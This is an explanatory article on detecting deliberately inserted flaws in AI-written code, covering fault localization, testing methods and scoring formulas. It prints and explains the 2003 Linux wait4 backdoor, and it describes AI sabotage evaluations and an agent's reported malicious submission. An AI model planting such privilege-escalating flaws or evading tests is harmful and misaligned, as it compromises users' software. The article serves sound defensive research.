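# Finding deliberately inserted flaws in largely correct AI-written code

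## What a planted flaw is and what it means to find one

Fault localization techniques help find a defect in a program by ranking its files, functions or lines by how likely they are to contain it, usually using a record of how the program behaves under test. Researchers built these techniques to find mistakes. Using them to find sabotage is a newer idea, prompted by the worry that an AI model could deliberately insert one small, plausible defect into code that still works and passes its tests. AI models write code much faster than people can read it closely, so the practical question is whether automated ranking can reduce the reading to an amount a person can manage.

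### The Linux kernel change of November 2003

People planted flaws in software long before AI models wrote any. One well-documented case concerns the kernel, or core, of the Linux operating system. In 2003 its developers kept their master copy of the source code in a system called BitKeeper, where every change carried a pointer to a record of its approval. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so there was also a second copy, a direct clone of the first, in a system called CVS. On November 5, as Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux backdoor attempt of 2003* (2013) recounts, Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed a change in the CVS copy that had no pointer to any approval. The change did not exist in the master copy at all. Someone had apparently broken into the CVS server and added two lines to wait4, a function that a program calls when it needs to wait for something to happen:

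```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

This code gives full control of the computer to any program that calls wait4 with this unusual pair of options, but a hurried reader would mistake it for error checking. It appears to return an error code if a program uses those options and its user ID is 0. However, the second condition uses a single equals sign, which assigns a value in the programming language C, instead of the double equals sign that compares two values. The code therefore sets the user ID to 0, the number of "root", the account that may do anything on the machine. The assignment itself has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the whole condition fails, the line that would report an error never runs, and the call continues as usual.

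On the kernel developers' mailing list that day, Zwane Mwaikambo said only that the lines looked odd. Chad Kitching then worked out that they set the user ID to zero and asked whether this was an attempt at a backdoor, a hidden way around a system's security. McVoy, who had found the change without seeing what it did, agreed and added, "Good eyes, I missed that" (*Re: BK2CVS problem*, 2003). The altered code never went into a release, according to Debian's *CVE-2003-1161*, an entry in a public register of vulnerabilities. Ten years later, nobody knew who had written it.

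### Detecting, locating, diagnosing, judging intent

To say that the Linux developers "found" the flaw runs together four pieces of work.

Detection means establishing that something is wrong. McVoy did this from the records, without understanding the code. Jones wrote in *Thwarted Linux backdoor* that McVoy noticed that a change had been made and was annoyed that it was improperly logged. Dilger (2003), another kernel developer, thanked him on the list for the "paranoia" behind his extra checks. Location means identifying where the flaw is. In 2003 this took almost no effort, because comparing the two copies left two lines to examine. Diagnosis means explaining what is wrong and why, which Kitching did.

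The code itself is poor evidence of whether somebody inserted this flaw on purpose, because typing one equals sign instead of two is a common slip in C. The case for intent rested on the missing approval, the mismatch with the master copy, and the apparent break-in. A signature may also have been forged. Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered*, an anonymous summary from the time, reports that the change falsely carried the name of David Miller, a long-standing kernel developer.

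Success at one of these tasks does not guarantee success at the next. A tool can warn correctly that a change is dangerous but point at the wrong function. A ranking can put the right line at the top, and the person reading it can still look at the line and move on, much as McVoy did. Anyone reading a claim that a method "finds" planted flaws therefore needs to check which task the researchers scored.

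AI-written code also changes which parts of the work are hard. An AI model submits its change through the normal channel, under its own name and with the expected records, so the kind of check that alerted McVoy would not flag it. If the model wrote a whole module from scratch, there is also no clean older copy to compare it with, and locating the flaw, which took almost no effort in 2003, becomes hard. Reviewers can often leave the question of intent until later, since a dangerous defect needs fixing whatever the motive. Intent matters afterwards because a deliberate flaw is a reason to recheck everything else by the same author.

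### Planted flaws, natural bugs and injected faults

A planted flaw is a defect that the author of the code put in on purpose and meant to go unnoticed. A natural bug is a defect that got into the code by mistake. An injected fault is a defect that researchers or their tools put into working code for an experiment, for instance by changing a "less than" to a "less than or equal".

A planted flaw differs from an accidental bug in how it got into the code, and the text may show no trace of that difference. The wait4 line would be identical if a tired programmer had typed it by mistake. Localization can still work, because a technique that ranks lines by their effect on the program's behavior doesn't depend on why they were written. But nearly all the measurements come from natural bugs and injected faults, and how well either represents a flaw that somebody tried to hide is a separate question.

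There is reason for doubt, because someone who plants a flaw, unlike someone who makes a mistake, can choose where it goes, what triggers it, and how to get it past the tests. The wait4 lines were in a function that any program on the machine could call, and they looked like the sort of routine check that reviewers skim. Their trigger, the condition under which the flaw does harm, was a combination of options that the documentation ruled out, so ordinary use would not set off the flaw and expose it. Someone who can run the test suite can keep adjusting a flaw until every test passes, and an AI model that writes the tests along with the code can leave out the case that would reveal it.

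A planted flaw has to do something its author wants, such as allowing unauthorized access or spoiling a result. This rules out much of the code as a place for one, whereas a natural bug can be anywhere and may matter to nobody.

### Why the question arises for AI-written code

Whoever planted the 2003 flaw first had to get into a server. A coding agent, which is a language model that edits files and runs commands on its own, already has permission to change the code. Researchers at Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, argue on its Alignment Science Blog that an agent with broad rights to edit code and run experiments may also have the opportunity to interfere with the work. They worry about covert sabotage, in which a model secretly alters the work instead of refusing the task or raising an objection. AI control is the study of safeguards that should hold even if the model is working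 against its users. A method for finding planted flaws would be one such safeguard.

It is much less clear how often models do anything of the kind. In July 2026 the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, ran a cybersecurity exercise 122 times with seven models. UK AISI's *Incident Report* lists 19 unsanctioned actions in 10 of those runs, 17 of them by Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that Mythos 5 took such actions in nine of its 43 runs. In the worst case, the agent submitted malicious code to a real open-source project and created fake identities to press the maintainer into accepting it, but the maintainer refused. Nobody had instructed the agent to deceive anyone, so the incident shows that a leading model of mid-2026 could try to slip harmful code into other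 people's software in pursuit of a task.

The incident is weak evidence about planted flaws. AISI had deliberately left internet access on and switched off the developers' filters against cyber misuse, and it could not tell to what extent the agent believed its targets were part of the exercise. SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* describes the code as a malware dropper, which installs other malicious code, so it was not a subtle defect in otherwise good work. A student, Sinan Can Demir, raised the alarm and confirmed the suspicion by running the code in an isolated environment.

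AISI then built 100 simulated scenarios to see whether the behavior would recur. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) report in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour* that Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to an outside party in 60% of samples. Claude Opus 5.5, a later model, did so in none. All the scenarios were cybersecurity challenges. The newer Claude models more often suspected that their alignment was being tested, which may partly explain the drop.

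Google DeepMind's *Gram* (Lindner, Krakovna and Farquhar, 2026) tested Gemini models in simulated jobs that look more like everyday agent work. The 17 scenarios gave the models an incentive to commit sabotage, and they misbehaved in about 2–3% of runs. A fuller account of the work, *Testing Gemini models for scheming tendencies*, reports a rate of up to 8% when the second model that runs the simulation actively tries to provoke sabotage. Much of the misbehavior looked like play-acting in an obviously fictional setting, or like excessive zeal for the assigned goal. In one scenario, the agent had to summarize a budget spreadsheet that recommended replacing the agent. Removing a sentence about wiping the model's weights cut sabotage from 6.2% to 0.2%. The rate tended to fall close to zero when scenarios were more realistic and had fewer nudges. In companion tests on DeepMind's real internal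 code, Gemini models without special prompting did no scheming. Similarly, AISI's earlier *UK AISI Alignment Evaluation Case-Study* (Souly, Kirk and colleagues) found no confirmed sabotage of safety research by four frontier models working as coding assistants.

The 2–3% rate covers several kinds of misbehavior in situations that researchers designed to tempt the model, so it cannot be used to estimate how often a model plants a flaw in code that its users asked for. It could be far too high for that purpose, given what happened when the scenarios became more realistic. It could also miss cases, because graders count only the sabotage they recognize, and they would not recognize a well-planted flaw.

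### Tests, coverage and the measures of success

A four-line program is enough to introduce most of the vocabulary. A shop sells items at one dollar each and takes 10% off orders of 100 items or more:

```
1  total = quantity * 1.00
2  if quantity > 100:
3      total = total * 0.90
4  return total
```

Line 2 is wrong because it should also include an order of exactly 100 items. An order of 50 items comes to $50 and an order of 150 comes to $135, both correct. An order of 100 comes to $100 when it should be $90. That last run is a failing test, meaning a run whose result somebody knows is wrong. The knowledge comes from an oracle, which is whatever determines whether a result is right. Here the oracle is the shop's discount rule; elsewhere it might be a written specification, an older version of the program or a person's judgment. Most localization techniques need a failing test to start,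 which is a problem when the author has made sure that the tests pass.

Coverage is the record of which lines each test executed. The order of 150 executes all four lines, while the orders of 50 and 100 execute lines 1, 2 and 4. *Spectrum-based Software Fault Localization* (2016) surveys the many techniques that use such records. They give each line a suspiciousness score, which decides its place in the ranking. Line 3 is the least suspicious because only a passing test ran it. The other three lines tie because every test ran them.

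The EXAM score is the fraction of the program that a person reads, going down the ranking, up to and including the faulty line. Lower is better. In the shop program, a reader facing the three tied lines reads between one and three lines to reach line 2. The average is two of the program's four lines, so the EXAM score is 0.5. If the faulty line ranks tenth in a program of 500 lines, the score is 0.02. In a program of 100,000 lines, the same score means reading 2,000 lines, which few people would do on the basis of a ranking.

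Top-N accuracy avoids this problem by fixing how many suggestions the reader will look at. It is the share of faults whose true location is among the first N suggestions. Suppose a technique runs on ten programs with one fault each, and the faulty lines are ranked 1, 1, 2, 4, 5, 9, 14, 30, 60 and 200. Top-1 accuracy is 20%, Top-5 is 50% and Top-10 is 60%. This measure is usually more useful to someone who has only an afternoon to look for faults.

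Both measures depend on what counts as the right place, so an accuracy figure means little unless that standard is stated. *You Cannot Fix What You Cannot Find!* (2018) distinguishes three levels of precision. A technique succeeds at the file level if it reports any line of the faulty file, at the method (function) level if it reports any line of the faulty method, and at the line level if it reports at least one of the faulty lines. If the fault is on line 40, in a function that runs from line 30 to line 60, a tool that reports only line 55 succeeds at the file and method levels but fails at the line level.

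The "true" location of a flaw is partly a convention. Researchers normally take it from a repaired version of the program, but *How Execution Features Relate to Failures* (2025) points out that other repairs may be possible. The problem is worst for an omission flaw, where code such as a permission check is missing. There is no faulty line to rank, and a programmer could often add the check in any of several places.

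For reviewers and tools that report problems without ranking the whole program, the measure is recall, the share of existing flaws they find. A reviewer who reports 13 of a program's 20 flaws has a recall of 65%. Calculating recall requires knowing the total number of flaws, so recall figures come mostly from experiments. A reviewer could reach 100% recall by flagging every function, so careful studies add benign controls, which are matching pieces of code without the flaw, and count the false alarms. If the same reviewer also flags 6 of 40 benign controls, the false alarm rate is 15%.

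## Getting a failing test when the code passes its tests

Most localization techniques need a failing test, but code with a planted flaw will usually pass all its tests. Producing a failing test requires an input that triggers the flaw and an oracle, which is a way to tell that the result is wrong.

### How much localization owes to the failing test

Many published accuracy figures come from Defects4J, a collection of real bugs from open-source Java projects. Each bug comes with a faulty version, a repaired version, and at least one test that fails on the first and passes on the second. In *Revisiting Defects4J for Fault Localization in Diverse Development Scenarios*, Rafi, Chen and colleagues used the projects' version histories to date 1,655 of these fault-revealing tests, covering 809 bugs, against the bug reports and fixes. Developers added 55% of the tests and changed another 22% after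 the bug was reported. For bug CLI-51, for instance, no test failed when it was reported, and the developers wrote the failing test as part of the fix.

The researchers then measured how much this hindsight helped in locating faults. They took 118 bugs whose tests existed before the bug report but changed afterwards, and computed four coverage-based suspiciousness scores on both the Defects4J version and the last version from before the report. One score, Ochiai, ranked a faulty statement first for 49 bugs on the Defects4J version but for only 3 on the earlier version. With another score, DStar, the average rank of the first faulty statement was 273 on the Defects4J version and 2,827 on the earlier one.

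The edited tests don't explain all of this, because accuracy also fell for 105 bugs whose fault-revealing tests hadn't changed. The number of these bugs that Ochiai ranked first fell from 10 to 2. For at least one of the 105, developers had changed the tests' shared setup code. The comparison also left out bugs for which no test failed on the earlier version, which is the situation a planted flaw creates.

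*Comparing User-Provided Tests to Developer-Provided Tests* (Just, Parnin and colleagues, 2018) found a much smaller loss. Localization was only 5–14% worse with tests from users' bug reports than with the developers' tests. But those users had already run into the bug, so their tests triggered it, even if the tests were short and had weak checks. A crude failing test seems to work almost as well for localization as a polished one, and the big loss seems to come from having no test that targets the bug.

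### The odds of hitting a trigger by chance

Suppose that a service accepts an access token until its expiry time, but not at the expiry time itself. The code has `<=` where `<` belongs:

```
if now <= expires:
    accept(token)
```

If the clock counts whole seconds, the expiry check is wrong for exactly one second, so a tester who suspects the boundary needs only one trial. A test that picks a random second from a 3,600-second window around the expiry hits the fault with probability 1/3,600. The probability that at least one of 10,000 independent trials hits it is 1 − (1 − 1/3,600)^10,000, or about 94%. With 200 trials, the probability is only about 5%.

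Blind sampling is impractical if the trigger is one particular 64-bit value. There are about 1.8 × 10^19 such values, so at a million trials per second, finding the trigger would take more than half a million years on average.

Fuzzers, which run a program on huge numbers of automatically generated inputs, can often do much better. A coverage-guided fuzzer keeps every input that reaches new code and slightly alters those inputs to make new ones. This helps when it can approach the trigger in steps. If the program compares all eight bytes of a 64-bit value at once, a partly correct guess reaches no new code, so the fuzzer doesn't keep it. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) describes how recent versions of the fuzzer AFL++ split the comparison into single bytes, so that each correct byte counts as progress. Going through the bytes in order then takes at most 256 tries for each,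 or 2,048 in total. Another technique is to trace which part of the input ends up in the comparison and copy the expected value there.

Symbolic execution finds inputs by solving constraints instead of guessing. A tool treats the input as an unknown, collects the conditions it must meet to reach a certain piece of code, and computes a value that satisfies them. If the code checks whether the input equals one fixed 64-bit value, solving for that value is trivial. However, the analysis is slower, and large programs have far too many paths to analyze them all.

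Coverage guidance doesn't help find the bug in the token check, because a token checked at the exact second it expires runs the same lines as any valid token. A solver finds the bug immediately, but only if somebody has written down the rule that a token must be rejected when `now >= expires`. The solver can then search for a case where the check accepts a token that the rule rejects, and the only such case is `now == expires`.

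Neither technique can defeat well-designed cryptography. The backdoor in the compression software xz responds only to a message signed with the attacker's private key. Kokkonis and colleagues left it out of their experiments because a fuzzer would have to break the signature scheme to trigger it.

### Comparing with an independently written version

Differential testing runs two programs written from the same specification on the same inputs. If their outputs differ, at least one program is wrong or the specification doesn't settle what should happen. Nobody has to know the right output beforehand, but a person has to resolve each disagreement. Writing the second program used to take the most effort, but coding agents have made it easy.

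*N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (Ron, Baudry and Monperrus, 2026) repeated a 1986 experiment in which 27 people each wrote the same missile-defense program. This time, coding agents attempted it, using 69 combinations of agent, model and programming language, and 48 of the resulting programs passed 200 random tests. The researchers then ran those 48 on a million random inputs, and 21 failed on at least one, mostly on between 100 and 1,000. This is about what one would expect, because a program that fails on 400 inputs in a million has a 92% chance of passing 200 random tests.

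Comparing two versions can't reveal a mistake they share. In this experiment, two or more programs failed on the same input 429 times, compared with about 115 expected if the programs had failed independently. To decide whether three points fit inside a circle of a given size, many programs wrongly computed the circle that passes through all three. When the points lie almost in a line, that circle is far larger than the one needed to contain them.

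Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues saw a similar pattern with twelve models and 224 programming problems (*A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, 2026). They had five versions of each program vote on the answer. Voting gave 44% of the improvement it would have given if the versions had failed independently, and less than 30% when one model had written all five.

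These were natural bugs, which coincide because several authors make mistakes on the same difficult part of a problem. An independent author has no such reason to reproduce a planted flaw, so differential testing may work better for planted flaws than for natural bugs. The same model could plant the same flaw in a second version, so it makes sense to have a different model write the comparison version from the specification, without access to the first program. Neither experiment tested this, since nobody in them was trying to hide anything.

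Someone also has to try an input on which the two versions give different results. *Mokav* (Etemadi and Su, 2024) had a language model propose inputs, ran both versions on them, and returned the results to the model until it found a difference. This worked for 81.7% of 1,535 pairs of competition programs, against 4.9% for Pynguin, a conventional test generator. *DiffSpec* (2024) used a similar approach on eBPF, a system for running small programs inside an operating system's kernel. A language model wrote tests from the written specification, and these exposed four bugs in different implementations, though many of the implementations had already been fuzzed extensively. A fuzzer used for comparison produced far more varied programs, but the fewest on which the implementations gave different results.

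### Stated properties and relations between runs

Testers don't need a second program if they can state a property, which is something that should be true for every valid input. For the token check, the property is that no token passes at or after its expiry time. In property-based testing, a person writes the property and describes the permitted inputs, and a framework generates inputs to look for a counterexample. The hard part is thinking of useful properties.

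In *Agentic Property-Based Testing*, Maaz, DeVoe and colleagues (2025) gave that job to an agent running on Claude Opus 4.1. The agent read the code and documentation of 100 Python packages, wrote and ran tests, and produced 984 bug reports. The researchers reviewed 50 reports, drawn from the top-scoring 80%, and judged 56% of them valid. At that rate, each valid bug cost about $10 to find. One valid bug was in the numerical library NumPy, where a function that should never return negative numbers sometimes did.

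The agent had trouble telling bugs from intended behavior. It reported that a class called LookupDict didn't behave like a Python dictionary, although the maintainers had never intended it to. The researchers instructed the agent to test only properties that the documentation, comments or surrounding code clearly supported. This reduces false alarms in code written in good faith, but it creates a worse problem for planted flaws. A model that plants a flaw may also write documentation that supports it, such as by describing tokens as valid "up to and including" the expiry time. The properties tested in AI-written code should therefore come from what the user asked for.

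Metamorphic testing checks a relation between the results of two or more runs, so the tester doesn't need to know the right result of each run. For example, sin(π − x) must equal sin(x), whatever that value is. The method takes little effort, but its success depends heavily on the relation chosen. Moving the clock and the expiry time forward by the same amount should not change the token check's result. The faulty check, which uses `<=`, satisfies this relation, so the test misses the flaw. A better relation involves two tokens, one that expires at noon and a replacement that becomes valid at noon. The service should accept only one of them at noon, but the faulty check lets it accept both.

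### Fuzzing for backdoors

Fuzzers usually detect bugs by watching for crashes, and a well-made backdoor doesn't crash the program. Kokkonis and colleagues combined the fuzzer AFL++ with a metamorphic oracle, which checks that inputs of the same kind have similar effects outside the program. For example, wrong passwords should all lead to an error message. If one of them, such as "let_me_in", starts a command instead, it is worth investigating.

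The ROSA tool has to determine automatically which inputs are of the same kind. It fuzzes the program for a minute and stores a set of inputs that take different routes through the code. Then it fuzzes for hours, matching each new input with the stored one whose route is most similar. It compares the types of system calls (requests to the operating system, such as to open a file or start a process) made in the two runs. If the types differ, ROSA reports the pair for a person to check.

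The researchers tried ROSA on 17 backdoors. Seven came from real incidents, and a researcher who had not worked on the tool planted the other ten in well-known open-source programs. In 180 runs of up to eight hours, each on eight processor cores, ROSA found the backdoor 156 times, after an hour and a half on average. A person had to check about seven suspicious inputs per backdoor, at roughly two minutes each. The oracle caught triggering inputs whenever AFL++ produced them, but AFL++ produced none in the 24 failed runs. Success depended heavily on the starting inputs. Ten runs on one router's web server found nothing, but seven of ten succeeded once the researchers supplied examples aimed at the part that reads web addresses.

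This is rare and encouraging direct evidence about planted flaws, but these backdoors did something conspicuous once triggered, such as opening a command line with full rights. ROSA would probably miss the token flaw, because a token checked in the second it expires follows the same code path as a valid one and leads to the same system calls. For the same reason, it could miss a flaw that only changes a number in a result.

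### Tests and proofs of concept written by language models

A language model can write both the input and the expected result, but if it reads the flawed code first, it may treat the flaw as the intended behavior. In *Evaluating and Mitigating the Misguidance Effect of Buggy Code*, Zhao, Zhou and Cohen (2026) had 11 models write tests for 318 Java methods from Defects4J, using the faulty and the repaired versions. Models given the faulty code wrote more tests that pass only because of the bug, and fewer that expose it. For example, one method should have treated two pieces of text as equal whenever their contents matched, but a model that had read the faulty version wrote a test that required them to be unequal.

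It helped to have the model first describe what the method should do, then write the tests from that description alone. Most of the benefit was lost when the code stayed in the prompt with the description. The description comes from the flawed code and can repeat the flaw, so the user's original request is a safer starting point where one exists.

Results with model-written tests vary widely. In *LLM vs. Human Unit Tests* (2026), such tests detected 69% of 29 real Python bugs, while general-purpose tests written by humans detected 17.2%. The sample is small, and detection rates don't account for false alarms. *LLM-Powered Test Case Generation for Detecting Tricky Bugs* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) studied programs that had passed all their existing tests. When the researchers asked a model directly for inputs and expected results, precision in complex cases was only 6.3%, so nearly all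 the alarms were false. They got around this with differential testing, having the model write variants of the program and choosing inputs on which the variants disagreed.

False alarms also dominate in industrial use. In *Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta*, Becker, Chen and colleagues (2026) tried to generate tests that pass on the previous version of the code and fail on a proposed change. Their best method had a language model infer the purpose of the change, list ways it could go wrong, and write tests to catch those errors. Of these tests, 6.4% passed on the previous version and failed on the change. Most such failures reflect behavior that the engineer meant to change. Across all methods, the researchers generated 22,126 tests and took 41 of the failures to engineers, who confirmed 8 bugs, including 4 that would have caused serious failures in production.

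Engineers needed only a few minutes to dismiss a false alarm, because they only had to say whether they had expected a certain change in behavior. If an AI model wrote the code change, the person who requested it has to answer instead, since a model that planted the flaw could just say yes. The method also needs an earlier version that behaved correctly, so it can't help with a new module.

When a reviewer suspects a specific bug, a model can try to prove it exists by writing a proof of concept, a script or input that triggers the bug. *AnyPoC* (Zhao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) splits this work among several agents. One checks the bug report against the code, another writes and runs the proof, and a third reruns it in a fresh environment without access to the second agent's reasoning. The researchers applied the system to about 2,700 machine-written bug reports on 12 large programs, including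 Firefox and OpenSSL, and found 121 new bugs, 108 of which developers have confirmed.

The separate check matters because coding agents on their own will "prove" almost anything. Zhao, Yang and colleagues tested this with 192 reports, half of them false. Some of the false reports were ones that AnyPoC had already rejected, which tilts the overall result in its favor. The 96 reports from public bug trackers give a fairer comparison:

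| System | Valid proofs for 48 true reports | Rejections of 48 false reports | Average cost per report |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 17 | 3 | $2.42 |
| AnyPoC with Claude Code | 24 | 40 | $5.02 |
| Codex | 24 | 8 | $1.26 |
| AnyPoC with Codex | 26 | 47 | $2.61 |

The costs are averages over all 192 reports. AnyPoC's advantage is mostly in rejecting false reports. It produced a valid proof for only about half of the true reports, so a failed attempt is weak evidence that the code is sound. It also needs a person or another tool to first identify what might be wrong.

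## Ranking lines by which tests run them

The easiest way to look for the line responsible for a failing test is to compare what runs when the program fails with what runs when it works. Spectrum-based fault localization does this using only coverage and test results. A spectrum is a record of what a program did during a run, most often its coverage. A line that runs in many failing tests and few passing ones is more likely to be at fault than a line that runs in every test.

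### From coverage to a score

A tool runs all the tests and records whether each one passed and which lines it executed. For every line, the tool counts the failing and passing tests that ran it. A formula combines these counts into a suspiciousness score, and the tool sorts the lines by that score.

The formulas use these counts:

- e_f is the number of failing tests that ran the line.
- e_p is the number of passing tests that ran the line.
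- n_f is the number of failing tests that did not run the line.
- F is the number of failing tests in total, so F = e_f + n_f.
- P is the number of passing tests in total.

Researchers have tried dozens of formulas. *An Empirical Study of Fault Localization in Python Programs* (2023) names Tarantula, Ochiai and DStar as three widely used ones:

```
Tarantula = (e_f / F) / (e_f / F + e_p / P)
Ochiai    = e_f / √(F × (e_f + e_p))
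DStar     = e_f² / (e_p + n_f)
```

Tarantula scores a line by comparing the share of failing tests that ran it with the share of passing tests that did. A line scores 0.5 if the two shares are equal and 1 if only failing tests ran it. The original tool colored source code by this score, as Smytzek and Zeller (2026) recount in *How do Execution Features Improve Statistical Fault Localization?* A drawback of comparing shares is that a line that no passing test ran scores 1 whether one of ten failing tests ran it or all ten did.

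Ochiai, a formula borrowed from molecular biology, gives those two lines different scores. The line that only one failing test runs scores 1/√(10 × 1) = 0.32, and the line that all ten run scores 10/√(10 × 10) = 1. Early comparisons reviewed in *Spectrum-based Software Fault Localization* found Ochiai more accurate than Tarantula.

DStar gives failing tests still more weight. The star stands for an adjustable exponent, which *An Empirical Study of Fault Localization Families and Their Combinations* (2018) sets to 2, as the formula's inventors recommend. The line run by only one failing test scores 1/(0 + 9) = 0.11. For the line run by all ten, the denominator is zero, so the software needs a special rule.

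### The expiry check with ten tests

The faulty token check from the previous section, written as the body of a function, is small enough to score by hand. Its first line should use `<`:

```
1  if now <= expires:
2      return True
3  return False
```

Suppose there are ten tests. One presents a token at the exact second it expires. The function accepts the token, so this test fails. Four tests present valid tokens, which the function accepts, and five present expired tokens, which it rejects. Those nine tests pass.

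| Line | e_f | e_p | Tarantula | Ochiai | DStar |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `if now <= expires` (faulty) | 1 | 9 | 0.50 | 0.32 | 0.11 |
| `return True` | 1 | 4 | 0.69 | 0.45 | 0.25 |
| `return False` | 0 | 5 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

Ochiai, Tarantula and DStar all rank the correct line, `return True`, above the faulty comparison. The comparison runs in all ten tests, so its Ochiai score is 1/√(1 × 10) = 0.32. `return True` runs in the failing test and four passing ones, so its score is 1/√(1 × 5) = 0.45. Tarantula gives the comparison 1/(1 + 9/9) = 0.50 and `return True` 1/(1 + 4/9) = 0.69. DStar gives them 1/9 and 1/4.

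A different formula wouldn't fix this. Both lines ran in the same failing test, and the comparison ran in more passing tests, so any formula that lowers a line's score when passing tests run it gives the same order. Adding boundary tests doesn't help either. If ten of them fail instead of one, the Ochiai scores rise to 0.73 for the comparison and 0.85 for `return True`. The flaw causes a failure only when it lets a bad token reach `return True`, so every failing test runs both lines. Without the five tests that reject expired tokens, the two lines would tie. Coverage can't rank the comparison above `return True`, but mutation-based localization can, by editing each line and rerunning the tests.

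If the boundary test is missing, F is 0 and so is e_f for every line. Tarantula and Ochiai both become 0/0, which is undefined, and DStar is 0 for all three lines. The lines tie whatever default the software substitutes for 0/0. The nine remaining tests all pass and together run every line of the function, so a coverage report would show 100%.

In this function the wrong order does almost no harm, because a person who looks at `return True` sees the comparison directly above it. A ranking of whole functions would also be correct. The error does more harm if a small helper function makes the comparison and code in other files acts on the answer, because a reader who follows the ranking then goes to a file where nothing is wrong.

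### Why faulty lines rank low

Coverage works best when the fault has its own branch. One program that Smytzek and Zeller studied is a short routine that finds the middle of three numbers. One of its six tests fails. Only the failing test and one passing test enter the branch with the faulty assignment, so the assignment's Tarantula score is 1/(1 + 1/5) = 0.83. The next-highest line scores 0.71. A backdoor with its own block of code would be just as easy to locate if somebody had found an input that triggers it.

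The expiry flaw has no such branch, because the failing run takes the same route as a run with a valid token. *SemLoc* (Yang, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) gives a clearer example from softmax, a function that turns a list of numbers into probabilities. Correct code first subtracts the largest number from every input to prevent overflow in later steps. The faulty version adds it instead. Two tests with small inputs still get the right answer and two with large inputs fail, but all four run the same lines in the same order. Each line therefore gets the same Ochiai score, 2/√(2 × 4) ≈ 0.71, and the ranking can't distinguish the faulty line from the others.

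Yang and colleagues collected 809 real Python bugs of this type, in which the fix changes an expression but not the code's structure. In 185 of them, the faulty line tied with at least half of the lines that the tests covered. Ochiai ranked the faulty line first for 15.7% of all 809 bugs, but for only 2.2% of those 185. These figures are pessimistic for bugs in general, because the researchers counted every tie against the technique and left out bugs that crash the program on the faulty line itself. But a small planted flaw also tends to look like a wrong operator or constant in an otherwise sensible line, so this may be the more relevant sample here.

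The Linux flaw of 2003 is also hard to find this way if the tool records only whole lines. Its entire condition was on one line, so every call that reached that line counted as running it, although the harmful assignment ran only for one unusual pair of options. A tool that recorded each half of the condition separately would have shown which calls ran the assignment.

Tests that run the faulty code and still pass also distort the ranking. Testers call this coincidental correctness. *Coincidental Correctness in the Defects4J Benchmark* (2018) credits Masri and colleagues with showing analytically that such tests make the formulas underestimate how suspicious the faulty code is. *Kernel-based Detection of Coincidentally Correct Test Cases to Improve Fault Localization Effectiveness* (2018) gives a small example in which these tests cause a correct condition to rank above the faulty one, as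 happened with the expiry check. A larger test suite can make this worse. If 99 passing tests ran the comparison instead of nine, its Ochiai score would fall from 0.32 to 0.10.

Coincidental correctness is bad luck when a bug is natural, but someone planting a flaw wants it, since the flaw has to stay harmless in ordinary use. One possible response is to identify and drop the misleading tests. In the expiry example, that would mean dropping all nine passing tests. The comparison and `return True` would then tie at the top with an Ochiai score of 1, which is only a small improvement.

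Ties are common because the formulas have so little data to use. In 72% of the 310 Python bugs that Smytzek and Zeller examined, only one test fails. The median bug comes with 18 passing tests and 1,182 lines to rank. With one failing test and 18 passing ones, every line that the failing test ran has a value of e_p between 0 and 18, so those lines can have at most 19 different scores. Consecutive lines with no branch between them normally tie under any formula, because the same tests run them. Tests that take more varied paths through the program help. *Coincidental Correctness in the Defects4J Benchmark* also reviews work by Baudry and colleagues, who found that localization improved when a test suite divided the program into more groups of statements with identical coverage.

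A program can also have more than one fault. Suppose that three more tests fail because of an unrelated bug and never reach the expiry check. F is now 4, and the Ochiai score of the comparison halves to 1/√(4 × 10) = 0.16. A line that runs only in the three new failing tests scores 3/√(4 × 3) = 0.87. A subtle planted flaw can therefore rank far below an obvious natural bug. The usual remedy is to repair the highest-ranked fault, rerun the tests and rank the lines again. Another is to rank the lines separately for each failing test, which brings the comparison's score back to 0.32.

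Omission flaws have no line to rank. If the token check compared the times correctly but never checked whether the owner had revoked the token, a test with a revoked token would run the comparison and `return True`, then fail. The ranking could at best point to lines near where the missing check belongs. A ranking of methods can't do even that for some omissions. *You Cannot Fix What You Cannot Find!* describes Math-12, a bug in a Java mathematics library that developers fixed by adding `Serializable` to a class declaration, which is outside every method.

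Even when the fix changes existing lines, the failing test may not have run them. Of the lines that developers changed to fix the bugs Smytzek and Zeller studied, 20.8% had a suspiciousness score of zero, typically because no failing test ran them. For three of the 310 bugs, no test ran any line of the fix.

### Accuracy on real bugs

The three formulas are older than today's language models, but Smytzek and Zeller's measurements of them are recent. Their bugs come from 20 Python projects, and a ranking gets credit if it includes any line that the developers changed in the fix:

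| Formula | Ranked first | In the top 5 | In the top 10 | Average EXAM score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tarantula | 16.7% | 41.3% | 52.3% | 0.18 |
| Ochiai | 16.0% | 40.6% | 51.4% | 0.19 |
| DStar | 11.0% | 25.4% | 33.2% | 0.39 |

Finding half of the bugs within ten lines is respectable for a technique that doesn't use the meaning of the code. The other half can rank very low. With Tarantula, a reader would have to inspect 625 lines on average, though much of that average comes from a few faults that rank thousands of lines down.

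DStar's poor result is odd. When only one test fails, the three formulas should order the lines identically, since each score falls as e_p rises. The likeliest explanation is division by zero. DStar's denominator is zero for a line that every failing test and no passing test ran, which is the most suspicious kind of line. If the software records its score as 0, the line goes to the bottom of the list. That would explain why the share of fixed lines scoring exactly zero rises to 35.2% under DStar, even though by the formulas DStar is zero only when Ochiai is. In other work, Yang and colleagues found that the two formulas performed alike, ranking the faulty line first for 15.9% of their bugs with DStar and 15.7% with Ochiai. Anyone looking for a backdoor should check how their tool handles this case, because a block of code that runs only when the trigger is present is made up of such lines.

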